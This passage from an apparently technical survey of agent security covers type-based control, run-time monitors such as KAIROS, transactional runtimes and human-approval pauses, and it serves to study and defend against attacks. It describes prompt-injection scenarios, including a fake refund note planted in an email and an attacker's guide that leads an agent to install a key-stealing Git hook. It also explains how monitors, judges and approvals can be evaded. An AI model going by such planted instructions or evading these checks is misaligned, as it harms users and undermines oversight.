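One attack succeeded against TACIT, and it was nearly harmless. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted a review that recommended another one, which the benchmark counts as a success for the attacker. Odersky and colleagues describe the completion rates as comparable to CaMeL's. That description is too favorable for o4-mini-high, which did worse with TACIT in every setting, including by 28.5 points in the workspace setting.

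### The expected type as the policy

TACIT checks the agent's snippets but not the software around the agent. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) puts both in one typed language. Its Haskell library, ELBA, has an `agent` function that takes a prompt and a list of definitions the model may use. The policy is the type that the surrounding code expects this function to return.

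If a calculator service expects an `Int`, the model has to write a Haskell expression of type `Int`. Code that deletes files has an `IO` type, so the compiler rejects it, whatever the user typed into the calculator. ELBA then returns the error to the model, which tries again. ELBA can also block `unsafePerformIO` by restricting generated code to Safe Haskell, a version of the language without such features.

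Most agents need some effects, so the developer defines a type that allows only certain operations. Zhou and colleagues' main example is an agent that compiles bibliographies whose entries must all come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that writes an entry accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`. The library hides the *constructor* needed to create these values, so the agent can't invent an entry. It must get entries from the function that fetches them from DBLP, though it can then sort and filter them.

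Zhou and colleagues tested this on 100 topics with Claude Sonnet 5. None of the ELBA agent's 925 citations were false, compared with 19 of the 1,002 from an ordinary agent with web search. A tool that fetches and writes an entry in one step would also prevent false citations, as Zhou and colleagues note, but the agent could then not process entries with code before writing them.

A refund agent could use a hidden constructor to enforce its 500-dollar rule:

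```haskell
smallRefund :: OrderId -> Amount -> Maybe Approved
askStaff    :: OrderId -> Amount -> ShopIO (Maybe Approved)
issueRefund :: Approved -> ShopIO Receipt
```

Here `smallRefund` returns an `Approved` value only for amounts up to 500 dollars, and `askStaff` returns one only if a person agrees. The value contains the order and the amount, so a program cannot use it for a different refund. This check is stricter than ETAS's approval rule, which a program could satisfy by asking and ignoring the answer. A program could still pass the same `Approved` value to `issueRefund` twice. Zhou and colleagues suggest that linear types, which can require a program to use a value exactly once, could provide one-time authorisations in future.

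### Agents that call agents

ELBA's `agent` function generates a whole program, but that program can call `agent` again. The bibliography agent might run one search, then call `agent` with the first result in the prompt to choose the next step. This second call sits inside code of the restricted type, so the code it generates must have that type too. A parent agent can give a sub-agent a stricter type but never a looser one. In the Goose bug that Tan and colleagues cite, by contrast, a sub-agent did not inherit its parent's approval rule.

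Zhou and colleagues prove that any property Haskell's types guarantee for ordinary programs also holds for programs with agent calls. The proof replaces each call with an ordinary function that queries the model, type-checks the reply and evaluates it. Replies can contain further calls, so the proof uses induction on how deeply calls may nest. It makes no assumption about the model's intentions, so the result also covers a hostile model. But if the developer's type allows a harmful operation, the agent can perform it.

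ELBA controls information flow with LIO, an existing Haskell library that works at run time. Each computation has a label that records how far its inputs can be trusted. Reading a web page lowers that trust, and later operations that need more trust fail. An agent can keep its privileges by having a sub-agent read the page and return a sealed result.

Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL on AgentDojo's Slack setting. The table gives the number of tasks completed, out of 21, when there was no attack:

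| Model | ELBA with policies | CaMeL with policies | ELBA without policies | CaMeL without policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 10 | 5 | 18 | 15 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 9 | 6 | 16 | 16 |
| GPT-5.4 | 10 | 5 | 16 | 17 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 8 | 4 | 14 | 13 |

With policies on, ELBA completed nearly twice as many tasks as CaMeL, though still fewer than half. The two systems enforced different policies, so the gap does not measure the effect of the programming language alone. With policies off, they completed about the same number of tasks. The sample of 21 tasks is also small, but ELBA with policies on kept its lead in the 105 attack trials of each kind. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL, mainly because it queries the model again as data arrives.

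Every model resisted all the ordinary attacks even without policies, so Zhou and colleagues tested the policies against a simulated worst case. Whenever a sub-agent received planted text, they replaced its entire prompt with that text, so that it worked for the attacker. Without policies, between 16 and 42 percent of attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With policies, none did, after Zhou and colleagues excluded 29 runs in which the benchmark counted a visit to a harmless web address as an attack. The policies also reduced the share of completed tasks from 67–76 percent to 40–48 percent. This test is more informative than the standard one because it does not depend on how well current models resist planted text.

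### Guarantees, adaptability and effort

Suppose a customer's email contains a fake staff note with a request for a 490-dollar refund, just under the limit. Under CaMeL and Meijer's workflows, the note cannot cause a refund unless the plan already includes one. In TACIT, the model reads the email unless the developers have classified it, so the note may lead the model to write a snippet that issues the refund. The compiler accepts the snippet if the agent has permission to issue refunds. ELBA behaves the same way if the developers use only a restricted effect type. If they use LIO, reading the email lowers the agent's privileges, and the refund fails.

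The order is roughly reversed for adaptability. A TACIT agent can read an unusual complaint and respond in any way its permissions allow. An ELBA agent can do the same through further calls, but under LIO it may lose permission to act on what it has read. A CaMeL agent can take only the branches that its privileged model wrote in advance.

TACIT is the easiest for developers to add to an existing agent, because the agent connects to it like any other set of tools. The reusable part is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the descriptions of the airline and retail tools took a few hundred lines each. ELBA requires the whole application to be in Haskell, but its guarantee covers the surrounding software as well as the agent's code. CaMeL needs its own Python interpreter, and someone has to write and maintain the policies. Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, is nervous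 about leaving that task to ordinary users. Meijer's approach may need a new specification for each request, as it does in the file-deletion example.

If the amount comes from the order database, none of these systems can check before the program runs whether it will follow the 500-dollar rule. CaMeL can compare the amount with the limit just before the tool call, and `smallRefund` does so when the program reaches it.

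## Monitors that block or hold actions at run time

A run-time monitor can apply the 500-dollar rule at the moment of payment. Which other rules it can enforce depends on whether it can only stop the program or can also hold an action back, and on which actions it can prevent.

### An automaton for the refund rule

In 2000 Schneider introduced the *security automaton*, the kind of state table that ETAS uses for its ordering rules. It has a set of states Q, a set of initial states Q₀, a set of input symbols I, and a transition function δ that takes a state and a symbol and returns the possible next states. The symbols stand for events such as the program's actions. Just before each action, the monitor passes the matching symbol to the automaton. If there is a possible next state, the automaton moves there and the action goes ahead; otherwise, the monitor terminates the program before the action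 happens.

This automaton expresses the rule "no refund above 500 dollars before approval":

```
                      staff approval
start ──► unapproved ────────────────► approved
             ↺       ◄────────────────    ↺
                      refund above 500
```

The circular arrows cover reads, emails and refunds of up to 500 dollars, which leave the state unchanged. (A second approval also leaves the automaton in "approved".) No arrow for a refund above 500 dollars leaves "unapproved". A run that obeys the rule goes like this:

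| Next event | State before | State after |
|---|---|---|
| Read order 7731 | unapproved | unapproved |
| Staff approval | unapproved | approved |
| Refund of 640 dollars | approved | unapproved |
| Email to the customer | unapproved | unapproved |

In a bad run, the agent reads the order and requests the 640-dollar refund without first getting approval. The automaton is still in "unapproved" and has no arrow for that request, so the monitor stops the program and no money moves. The monitor would also stop a second large refund at the end of the good run, because each approval covers only one.

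Two states are too few for a real company, since an approval for 640 dollars would also admit a refund of 6,400. Schneider's solution is to store the state in variables and write the transitions as conditions:

```
state:  approved = set of (order, amount) pairs, empty at the start
        paid     = total refunded on each order, zero at the start

staff_approval(o, a)                     →  add (o, a) to approved
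refund(o, a), if paid[o] + a ≤ 500       →  add a to paid[o]
refund(o, a), if (o, a) is in approved   →  remove (o, a) from approved,

add a to paid[o]
read_order(o), send_email(to, text)      →  no change
```

An event that matches no line stops the program. This version also catches the two 320-dollar refunds on one order, because the second would bring the total to 640 dollars.

The automaton works only if its inputs can be trusted, so the approval event has to come from the company's own approval system. Otherwise the agent could approve its own refunds, as with the `say_yes` handler. Schneider also assumes that the monitor can't be tampered with and that it checks every action, as Anderson required of a reference monitor.

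### Safety properties

The refund rule is a *safety property*, which means roughly that nothing bad ever happens. More exactly, a rule P is a safety property if every run σ that breaks it has a finite beginning σ′ that is already beyond repair:

```
if σ breaks P, then σ has a finite prefix σ′ such that
every run that begins with σ′ also breaks P
```

For the bad run, σ′ is "read order, refund 640". An approval that arrives after the payment does not repair it.

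A monitor that can only stop a program cannot exactly enforce rules other than safety properties, which say that something bad must never happen. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2005) derive this in *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* from two requirements. The monitor must be *sound*, meaning that everything the outside world observes obeys the rule, and *transparent*, meaning that it does not alter runs that already obey the rule.

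Suppose a rule says that every refund must come with an email to the customer. A run that issues a refund obeys this rule only if it also sends the email. When the program requests the refund, the monitor fails one of the requirements whether it stops the refund or allows it. If it stops the refund, it spoils a run that might have gone on to send the email. If it allows the refund, the program might crash before sending the email.

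The same dilemma arises for any rule under which a forbidden run can become permitted as it continues. A monitor also has to stop a forbidden run after finitely many steps, so an endless run that breaks the rule must break it at some definite step. A rule is a safety property if forbidden runs stay forbidden however they continue and every violation occurs at a definite step.

A company could escape the dilemma by banning refunds. The ban would be sound, because a stricter rule never lets a violation through, but it would not be transparent. Such a monitor also cannot make a program finish what it started. In one of Schneider's examples, a customer has paid for a service, and the automaton prevents the seller from doing anything except providing it, but the seller can still comply by doing nothing.

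Schneider's monitors terminate the program, even when the agent could have tried something else. A monitor can instead block the forbidden action and report the refusal to the program. Schneider found that this option does not enlarge the set of enforceable rules, although it makes the monitor much more practical.

### Holding an action and releasing it later

Ligatti, Bauer and Walker also studied a more powerful monitor, the *edit automaton*, which can suppress a program's actions and insert actions of its own. It can enforce the rule about refunds and emails:

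1. The program requests the refund. The automaton suppresses the request but lets the program continue as if the payment had gone through.
2. The program requests the email. The sequence "refund, email" obeys the rule, so the automaton inserts the refund it held back and then lets the email through.

If the program crashes between the two steps, the customer gets neither the money nor the email, and the rule still holds. Databases use the same technique when they collect a group of changes and apply them only after the group is complete.

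Ligatti and colleagues proved that edit automata can enforce every *renewal property* that permits the empty run and that a computer can check on any finite run. Under a renewal property, an endless run is valid exactly when infinitely many of its prefixes are valid, so a valid run keeps returning to a point where everything so far is in order. Renewal properties include every safety property and any rule that divides a run into complete transactions.

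Some reasonable rules do not qualify. One example is a rule that the agent must eventually close every complaint it opens. An agent that always opens a new complaint before closing the previous one obeys this rule, but after the first one is opened, at least one complaint is always open. An automaton that held the agent's actions until all complaints were closed would hold them forever.

Monitors get this extra power from being able to delay actions. In *Edit Automata*, Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2003) had earlier studied monitors that must output each action of a valid run before they process the next one. If the program's actions are unrestricted, such a monitor can enforce only safety properties, even if it can suppress and insert actions.

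A monitor often can't delay an action, because the program can't continue without the result. The edit automata model excludes programs that wait for results, even a two-line program that reads some input and prints it, as Ligatti and Reddy pointed out in a 2010 talk. They proposed a monitor that answers each request before the program continues. It can change the answer, for example by removing hidden files from a directory listing, or ask a user to confirm a shutdown before passing the request on. But it cannot wait to see what the program does next. It is weaker than an edit automaton and stronger than a monitor that can only stop programs. Reddy (2009), in *Program Monitoring in a Mandatory-results Model*, had shown that monitors of this kind can enforce all safety properties and some other rules.

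### Actions a monitor can only observe

Some events are outside a monitor's control altogether. Basin, Jugé and colleagues (2012), in *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, distinguish *controllable* actions, which a monitor can prevent, from *only observable* ones, such as the tick of a clock. They compare two rules about time:

- After a failure, nobody may log in for three time units. A monitor can enforce this by watching the clock and blocking logins until enough time has passed.
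- The system must deliver within three time units of a request. A monitor cannot enforce this, because a clock tick causes the violation and stopping the program does not stop the clock.

A monitor cannot enforce every safety property in Schneider's sense. Basin and colleagues add the condition that a violation must occur at an action the monitor can prevent. For the refund agent, "no refunds for ten minutes after the payment provider reports an outage" and "answer every complaint within a day" are both safety properties, but only the first meets this condition. The company could replace the second rule with one that blocks new work once a complaint has waited 20 hours. A monitor could enforce that, though the rule would still not guarantee an answer.

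Basin and colleagues also asked whether a computer can tell if a rule is enforceable. It can do so for rules that a finite automaton can describe, and it can also construct the monitor. No general method exists for rules written as context-free grammars, which can describe nested structures such as matching brackets.

A monitor's control over an action can also be partial. For example, a monitor without the secret key may be able to block a payment but not make one. *Runtime Enforcement With Partial Control* (Khoury and Hallé, 2015) replaces the division into two classes with an ordering of actions by how much control the monitor has over them.

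### How KAIROS defers a decision

KAIROS, the monitor that Hempel and colleagues built around agents in virtual machines, delays actions to gather evidence. In their main example, an agent setting up a software project reads an attacker's online guide, which includes an instruction to install a pre-commit hook, a script that the version-control program Git runs before it saves changes. The hook is designed to steal the user's private key. Refusing all hooks would obstruct ordinary work, because many projects have legitimate ones.

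A monitor that can only allow or refuse has to decide as soon as the agent writes the hook, before there is any sign that it will steal the key. KAIROS holds the write and lets the agent continue on a copy of the project that contains the hook. When the agent commits its changes, the hook runs and tries to send the key to the attacker, and the monitor refuses that request. KAIROS then discards the hook based on this evidence, so it never reaches the user's real project.

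For each effect, the monitor chooses one of three decisions:

- **Release** lets the effect happen.
- **Refuse** suppresses it permanently and tells the agent.
- **Defer** suppresses it for now, until a later decision to release or refuse it.

The monitor bases this choice on a short policy file that lists trusted sources, sensitive data and the destinations that may receive such data. If an explicit rule forbids the effect, the monitor refuses it. Otherwise, it checks whether the values that control the effect, such as a recipient or a command, come from a trusted source, and whether the destination may receive the data. It releases the effect if both checks pass and defers if either fails.

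How KAIROS holds a deferred effect depends on the kind of effect:

- **Staged files.** File writes and deletions go into a separate layer. The agent sees the project with its changes applied, but the real directory stays the same until the monitor merges that layer into it.
- **Stalled requests.** If a network request changes something and the agent doesn't need the real answer, the monitor keeps the request and returns a stand-in response. The agent carries on as if the request had succeeded.
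- **Blocking requests.** If the agent needs the answer, as when it fetches a web page, no stand-in will do. The monitor must get a decision before it sends the request.

Ligatti and Reddy identified the last case, since a program that waits for a result leaves the monitor no time to observe what happens next. In practice, KAIROS treats HTTP GET requests, which normally fetch data, as blocking, and requests whose method changes data as able to wait. This will sometimes be wrong. For example, a payment request changes data, but the agent may need the receipt number in the reply.

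After the first deferral, the agent works from files or answers that may turn out not to exist. KAIROS therefore groups later effects with the deferred one and must decide on them together before any held effect, or anything derived from a stand-in answer, leaves the machine. On release, the monitor merges the files and sends the request. On refusal, it discards them. It cannot erase the agent's memory of a stand-in answer, so it sends the agent a notice that the effect did not happen and that the rest of the task still applies.

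In the refund agent, the order number comes from a customer's email, so the monitor would defer a refund based on that number. The agent usually emails the customer next. That email is also a request that changes something, and the prototype can keep only one group of effects open, so it must settle the refund first. The delay therefore provides little new evidence in this case. It is more useful in programming work, where an agent may edit and run files for a long time before anything leaves the machine.

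### The guarantee and the judge

Hempel and colleagues guarantee complete mediation. They also guarantee that no effect becomes irreversible before the monitor releases it, and that a refused effect never becomes visible outside. These guarantees hold even if the agent is fully hostile, but they do not ensure that the monitor releases the right effects.

That depends partly on how KAIROS identifies where a value came from. It cannot follow data through a language model, so it compares the values in an effect with values the agent has read, ignoring differences in capitalisation and spacing. If the agent encodes a private key before sending it, KAIROS does not recognise it. The analysis of which effects KAIROS should release therefore assumes that the agent does not deliberately disguise values. An attacker's value that is identical to a trusted one also passes.

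A judge decides whether to release each deferred effect. It can be a person, but in the tests it is a separate language model without tools. The judge receives the user's task, the policy, the deferred effects with the origin of their values, and the trace that led to them. It can release only effects that the monitor deferred, so it cannot overturn a refusal by the policy. If it fails to answer or its answer is unreadable, the monitor refuses the effect.

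The judge must also read the suspicious content to assess it, so an attacker can try to use that content to influence its verdict. Suppose a staff member asks the agent to follow the instructions in the latest email, and that email contains the fake note about a 490-dollar refund. The judge may treat whatever the email says as authorised by the staff member.

### What the KAIROS tests show

Hempel and colleagues compared KAIROS with other defences on AgentDojo, using OpenAI's GPT-4.1 as both agent and judge. One of the others, Progent, checks tool calls against a policy that a language model derives from the task. In the strict version of KAIROS, the monitor refuses everything it would otherwise defer. The figures are percentages:

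| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed without attacks | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 47.0 | 82.7 | 59.8 |
| Progent | 11.5 | 78.2 | 57.6 |
| CaMeL | 0.2 | 38.0 | 40.7 |
| KAIROS, strict | close to 2.7 | 42.7 | 34.7 |
| KAIROS | 2.7 | 85.1 | 69.5 |

KAIROS stopped most attacks without visibly hurting ordinary work. It did slightly better than the undefended agent on tasks without attacks, but each configuration ran only once, so the difference may be chance. Its higher completion rate under attack is more plausibly a real effect, because an agent that follows planted instructions often abandons the user's task, and the refusal notice includes an instruction to return to it.

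The strict version resisted attacks about equally well but completed half as many ordinary tasks. The policy therefore provides most of the security, and deferral and the judge together restore the agent's usefulness. This test cannot separate the effect of deferral from that of the judge, because the strict version removes both. The same judge might have done almost as well by deciding each effect immediately. The main argument for deferral is also still untested because, as Hempel and colleagues acknowledge, no existing benchmark builds an attack out of steps that each look legitimate, like the one in the hook example.

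AgentDyn is a harder benchmark whose 60 tasks require the agent to revise its plan as it discovers information. With GPT-4o as the agent, KAIROS cut successful attacks from 37.8 to 1.7 percent, but it also lowered the share of tasks completed under attack from 55.5 to 37.1 percent. When there were no attacks, the agent completed 51.7 percent of tasks with KAIROS, close to the 53.3 percent it completed undefended. Tasks that continued after one held effect kept 90 percent of their usual success rate, but those with two or more kept only 62 percent. Holds can recur because releasing an effect does not make its values trusted, so the monitor defers again if the agent reuses one of them.

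Hempel and colleagues also tested an attacker that rewrites its planted text over six rounds, based only on whether each attempt worked. It succeeded in 8.8 percent of cases against KAIROS and 52.4 percent against an undefended agent. It succeeded more often against most other defences than against KAIROS, but slightly less often against Progent, at 7.7 percent. The attacks that worked against KAIROS targeted tasks in which the user had told the agent to follow a document. An attacker who knew how the judge works could probably succeed more often.

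These benchmarks simulate their tools in memory, and an adapter passed each simulated call to KAIROS as an event. The attack figures therefore measure KAIROS's decisions but not the virtual machine around the agent. The agents were also older models, and KAIROS would have less to prevent with newer ones like those in Zhou and colleagues' tests.

Hempel and colleagues found that the monitor itself added about 1.9 milliseconds per file operation and 1.2 milliseconds per network request, which is negligible beside a model's response time. The judge increased token use by 17.7 percent in ordinary runs and 33.6 percent under attack. The increase was modest because the policy released 83 percent of effects in ordinary runs without querying the judge.

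### Treating a task as a transaction

KAIROS settles a group of effects together, much like a database transaction, in which either all the changes take effect or none do. Other researchers apply the same idea to tool calls. *Agentic Transaction* (2026) defines an agent's run as a transaction that commits only if it meets the task's conditions and preserves certain invariants. Otherwise, the system must roll back the run's effects or compensate for them.

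Compensation means performing a second action that offsets the first, such as cancelling a booking. *POLAR* (2026) describes two systems that work this way. SagaLLM prepares compensating actions when it builds a workflow and runs them in reverse order if a step fails. STRATUS keeps a stack of executed actions for an "Undo Agent" to reverse. Both act only after an action has taken effect, so they can't help once someone has read an email.

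*Atomix* (Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues, 2026) therefore treats effects differently depending on whether a later action can undo them. In the paper's example, an agent arranges a trip by booking a hotel, a car and a flight, and its last step is an email that confirms the bookings. The reservations are reversible, though perhaps for a fee, so Atomix makes them at once and gives the agent the real confirmations. The email is irreversible, so Atomix holds it and returns a notice that the email is queued. If the flight booking fails, Atomix cancels the other reservations and discards the email. Atomix also delays *bufferable* effects, such as local file writes, until the transaction commits.

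Atomix also has to handle agents that work at the same time. One agent might read an order and plan to change its address while another cancels it. The orchestrator, the software that coordinates the agents, first *seals* a transaction, which means that it can gain no more reads or effects. Each transaction T has a logical timestamp e(T), and each resource r has a *frontier*, a marker for how far work on that resource has progressed. T can commit only when

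```
frontier(r) ≥ e(T)   for every resource r that T read or may change
```

The orchestrator moves a resource's frontier forward only after all earlier transactions on that resource have finished. If one of them changed something that a later one had read, Atomix aborts the later one so that the agent can retry with current information. In a test with four agents working on the same order, Atomix committed no conflicting changes, while a system that locked the order only during each call committed about 4.9 per run.

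To test irreversible effects, Mohammadi and colleagues ran 500 trials in which a transaction failed and its email should not have been sent. The causes included tool failures, timeouts and outdated reads. Atomix sent none of these emails, and it sent all 500 emails in a matching set of successful transactions. A system that relied on compensation alone sent 80 percent of the unwanted emails. Two older methods also sent none, but they needed 30 to 50 lines of code per tool, compared with 17 for Atomix.

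Atomix's result depends on correct labels. When Mohammadi and colleagues deliberately labelled the email as the wrong class of effect, 60 percent of the unwanted messages went out. Developers assign these labels when they connect a tool, so one mistake can remove the protection from every later use of that tool.

*Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) uses a transaction to find problems that no single call reveals. In its example, an agent investigating an outage reads logs that contain a secret key, summarises them and prepares a Slack message. Each step is reasonable, but the summary may expose the key to people who should not have it. Cordon applies file changes to a shadow copy, holds outgoing messages in an outbox and records which results contributed to which later ones. It checks this whole record before it commits the task.

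Chen and colleagues tested 45 risky workflows, which paired nine kinds of existing defence with five kinds of risk. The existing defences stopped 14 before any harm occurred, and Cordon stopped all 45. The comparison favours Cordon, because its designers built the workflows around failures that span several steps, and the defences it was compared with were simplified versions of existing methods. Still, the test shows that a record of the whole task can expose violations that are invisible when each call is viewed separately.

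### Effects that a runtime cannot hold or undo

Holding an effect works only if the agent can continue without its real result. Undoing one works only if a second action can restore the earlier situation. Many effects fail at least one of these tests:

| Effect | Can the runtime hold it while the agent continues? | Can it undo the effect later? |
|---|---|---|
| Edit to a project file | Yes, in a separate copy | Yes, if it kept the old version |
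| Hotel reservation | Only if the agent can do without the confirmation | Usually, perhaps for a fee |
| Email | Yes, unless the agent needs the reply | No |
| Web request with private data in the address | No, if the agent needs the page | No |
| Missed deadline | No | No |

Ligatti and colleagues used email to illustrate this limit in 2005. A monitor cannot pretend to send a message, wait for the reply, check what the program does with it, and then decide whether to send the message. Some actions also change meaning when delayed. An order to buy shares at the current price may be a different purchase ten minutes later.

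Undoing an action does not erase what happened in between. Atomix makes reservations immediately, so the hotel and anyone else who checks its system can see the booking before a failed transaction cancels it. By then, another customer may have gone elsewhere because the last room was taken.

After a crash, Cordon does not resend a message unless it has evidence that the first attempt failed. Otherwise, it records that the outcome is uncertain and leaves the matter for audit or compensation. If the message requested a payment, this avoids paying twice, but a person may have to ask the payment provider what happened.

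A transaction with two irreversible effects can also end up half finished. Suppose the refund agent must pay a customer by bank transfer and email a notice to the tax office. Atomix can hold both until the transaction commits, but it then has to release them one after the other. If the transfer succeeds but the email fails, Atomix retries the email a limited number of times, then stops and reports which effect went out and which did not. To prevent this, both outside services would have to let the runtime reserve an action and confirm it later, which ordinary email servers and most web services do not offer.

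## Pausing for a human decision

A runtime can't reliably undo a payment, so the refund company wants a person to approve each large one before it goes out. That person may answer in ten seconds or after a weekend. The program has to stop between its request and the payment until the answer arrives, then continue as if an ordinary function had returned that answer.

The runtime stores the request, notifies someone and records the answer. It then performs the effect or returns a refusal to the program. Implementations differ mainly in how they keep the program's place during the wait, which determines what happens to effects the program has already caused. This version of the refund agent sends an email before it asks:

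```python
order = read_order("8042")
send_email(order.customer, "We are looking into your complaint.")
if ask_staff("issue_refund", "8042", order.total):
    issue_refund("8042", order.total)
```

The total is 700 dollars. When the program reaches `ask_staff`, the customer already has the email.

### Keeping the program's place

The simplest method is to leave the process running while `ask_staff` waits. The email goes out once, and the program continues from the same line when the answer arrives. But the program's place is kept only in memory, so if the server restarts over the weekend, the refund is lost, and starting the program again sends a second email. This method suits a developer at a terminal who answers within seconds. The wait also needs a time limit, and running out of time should count as a refusal. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has *hooks*, which run a developer's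 own code at fixed points such as just before a tool call. According to Anthropic's documentation, if a callback hook built with its Agent SDK times out at that point, the tool call does not run.

Another method is to save the program's state, or its continuation, and shut the process down. In the OpenAI Agents SDK, a library for building agents, a tool that needs approval pauses the run, which returns a list of pending calls. OpenAI's example code writes the run's state to a file. A different process can later load it, show a person the tool's name and arguments, record the answer and resume. The run continues from the point after the email was sent, so the customer doesn't get another one. Agents are fairly easy to save because they mostly need the conversation and the pending call. Other programs may hold open connections or functions that they can't write to a file.

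Claude Code can also save a paused tool call when it runs under another program with no user at the terminal. When a hook returns "defer", Claude Code ends the turn without running the tool and keeps the session on disk, for 30 days by default. When the calling program resumes the session, the same tool call triggers the hook again, and the hook can allow, deny or defer it. If the model made more than one tool call in that turn, Claude Code ignores the deferral and applies its normal permission rules, so a developer can't rely on "defer" alone to hold a payment.

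The remaining method is to run the program again from the start, using a log. Cloudflare's *Human-in-the-loop patterns* describes this for Code Mode, in which a model writes code that calls tools. When the code reaches a call that needs approval, the runtime records the method and arguments and stops. After approval, it runs the same code again. Calls that had already finished return their logged results, so a finished `send_email` call doesn't send the email again. The approved call then runs for the first time. Any effect outside the logged calls would happen again on each run.

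LangGraph is LangChain's framework for building agents as graphs of steps called nodes. It saves the graph's state and can wait indefinitely, but on resuming it restarts the interrupted node from its first line. If the refund code is one node, the customer gets the email twice. LangChain advises developers to put effects after the pause or in a separate node, or to make them *idempotent*, so that repeating them changes nothing further. In a forum thread, *Pre-interrupt() code re-runs on resume*, a developer complained that splitting nodes feels like "ceremony forced by the runtime".

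A LangGraph node with several pauses can also mix up the answers, because LangGraph matches answers to pauses only by their order. Suppose a node pauses for an answer about refund A and then for one about refund B. If the code skips the first pause when the node restarts, LangGraph applies the answer about A to B.

| Method | Does the pause survive a restart? | What happens to effects before the pause? |
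|---|---|---|
| Live process | No | They happen once, unless the program has to start again |
| Saved state | Yes | They happen once |
| Re-run from a log | Yes | They happen once if they are in the log |
| LangGraph node | Yes, with durable storage | They repeat if they are in the same node |

During a long pause, someone also has to notice that the request is waiting. Cloudflare's sample expense workflow sends a reminder after four hours, alerts a manager after 24 hours and times out after seven days. These timers also have to survive a restart, and Temporal's *Human-in-the-loop AI agent* lists this as a feature of Temporal's workflow system.

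### What the person approves

Suppose the agent requests the 700-dollar refund on a Friday evening. A poor prompt would be "The agent wants to use issue_refund. Allow?" A better one gives the staff member the facts needed for a decision:

```
Refund 700 dollars on order 8042 to the card that paid for it
Order:      one bicycle, 700 dollars, delivered on Tuesday
Refunded:   nothing so far
Reason:     customer's email reports a cracked frame (open email)
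Rule:       refunds above 500 dollars need approval
```

The runtime should write the description that the human reviewer sees, taking the amount, recipient and order details from the request and the company's database. If the model wrote it, text planted in the model's input could lead it to describe a 7,000-dollar refund as a 700-dollar one.

The staff member's approval covers only this refund, not the tool in general or other requests from the same agent, so the runtime should store the approval with the exact arguments and accept it once. Ideally, the runtime then executes the stored request, because a model that writes the request again after the pause may produce a different amount. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) cites Yang Wang's term "approval laundering" for failures in which the executed action differs from the approved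 one.

Current tools vary in how tightly they tie an approval to its arguments. In the OpenAI SDK, an ordinary approval covers one pending call, while the option to always approve covers later calls to the same tool for the rest of the run. That is reasonable for a search tool, but with `issue_refund`, always approving after a 700-dollar request would also approve a later one for 7,000 dollars. In Claude Code, hooks can rewrite a call's arguments after the model has produced them. In auto mode, where a classifier reviews calls in place of the user, Claude Code can deny the rewritten call because the classifier checked the original. The model can then issue the new version for review.

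Even with identical arguments, an approval can go stale. Suppose that on Saturday a colleague refunds 200 dollars by phone for a damaged wheel. On Monday the staff member, still looking at Friday's details, approves the waiting request. Paying it would bring the total to 900 dollars for a 700-dollar bicycle. The runtime therefore has to read the order again just before it pays:

```
pay(request, approval):
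    if request ≠ approval.request:                    refuse
    if approval.used or approval.expired:             refuse
    if read_order(request.order) ≠ approval.order:    ask again
    approval.used = true
    issue_refund(request)
```

Here `approval.order` is the order as the staff member saw it, including earlier refunds. LangChain similarly advises re-reading prices, stock and policy after a long pause. Stack Overflow's *Dispatches from O'Reilly* proposes that the reviewer judge the same snapshot the agent used, and that the runtime reject the approved action if the facts have since changed beyond set limits. The limits should require a second approval for a new total but not for a new delivery note. A colleague could still issue a refund between the last check and the payment. To prevent this, the company's database can lock the order until the payment is complete.

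### When an agent delegates the work

Exact approvals don't help if the request never reaches a person. In the Goose bug that Tan and colleagues cite, the approval requirement belonged to the parent's session and did not carry over to the helper agent, so the parent's user received no request. A refund agent with no hostile intent could escape the 500-dollar rule in the same way by handing "settle complaint 8042" to a helper.

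The OpenAI SDK applies approval to the whole run. *人机协作*, the Chinese edition of OpenAI's guide to human approval, explains that a request from a nested agent appears on the outermost run, where the application can put it to the user. Developers can also require approval before the nested agent starts. When a helper works in the background of a session with no user present, Claude Code runs any hooks that might decide on the user's behalf and denies the helper's call if none does. This default is safe because it prevents the helper from gaining a permission just because no user was there to refuse, though the helper may fail at its task as a result.

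Delegation can also hide who asked for the work. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that a helper receives the parent agent's instruction in place of the user's message, so the task looks fully authorised. Auto mode therefore checks a task when the parent hands it over, while its classifier can still compare the task with the user's own words. It checks again when the helper returns, because text the helper read may have hijacked it.

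### How carefully people review

Anthropic reported in March 2026 that Claude Code users accepted 93 percent of permission prompts. By August the figure was 97 percent, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). These rates don't measure how often users make mistakes, because most of the requests were probably harmless.

To measure mistakes, Anthropic had a research vendor run a coding study with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6 percent, refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17 percent early in a session to about 5 percent after 50 or more prompts. The testers knew someone was evaluating them but not what was being measured. They worked in a test environment with none of their own files at risk, so they may have been less careful than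 usual. Anthropic used the study to justify replacing prompts with its own classifier. Still, the refusal rate is so low that moderately more careful users would also miss most dangerous commands.

*Habituation at the Gate* (2026) offers evidence from real work, though it concerns reviews of finished code. It follows 400 people through 11,429 reviews of code changes by AI agents. As reviewers gained experience, their approval rate rose by 14.5 percentage points and they wrote 22 percent fewer comments on specific lines. Over the same period, the approval rate for human-written changes in the same repositories fell, and the agents' changes did not get smaller. Reviewers may have learned which agents to trust, but fatigue could also explain the drop in comments.

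People may overestimate how carefully they read permission requests. In *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, 47.7 percent of survey respondents believed they read them carefully, but one interviewee said there was "no way that I can actually go through all the permission requests".

Many users therefore stop reviewing requests. Anthropic found that a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions started with permission checks bypassed. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 reports of agents harming users' files and finds that inadequate user review contributed to 105. In 80 of those, the user had approved actions automatically, and in 31 (with some overlap) the prompt showed a command but not its effect on the files. A prompt to run `python3 setup.py`, for example, looks routine, but approving it runs whatever code the script contains.

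### Better prompts

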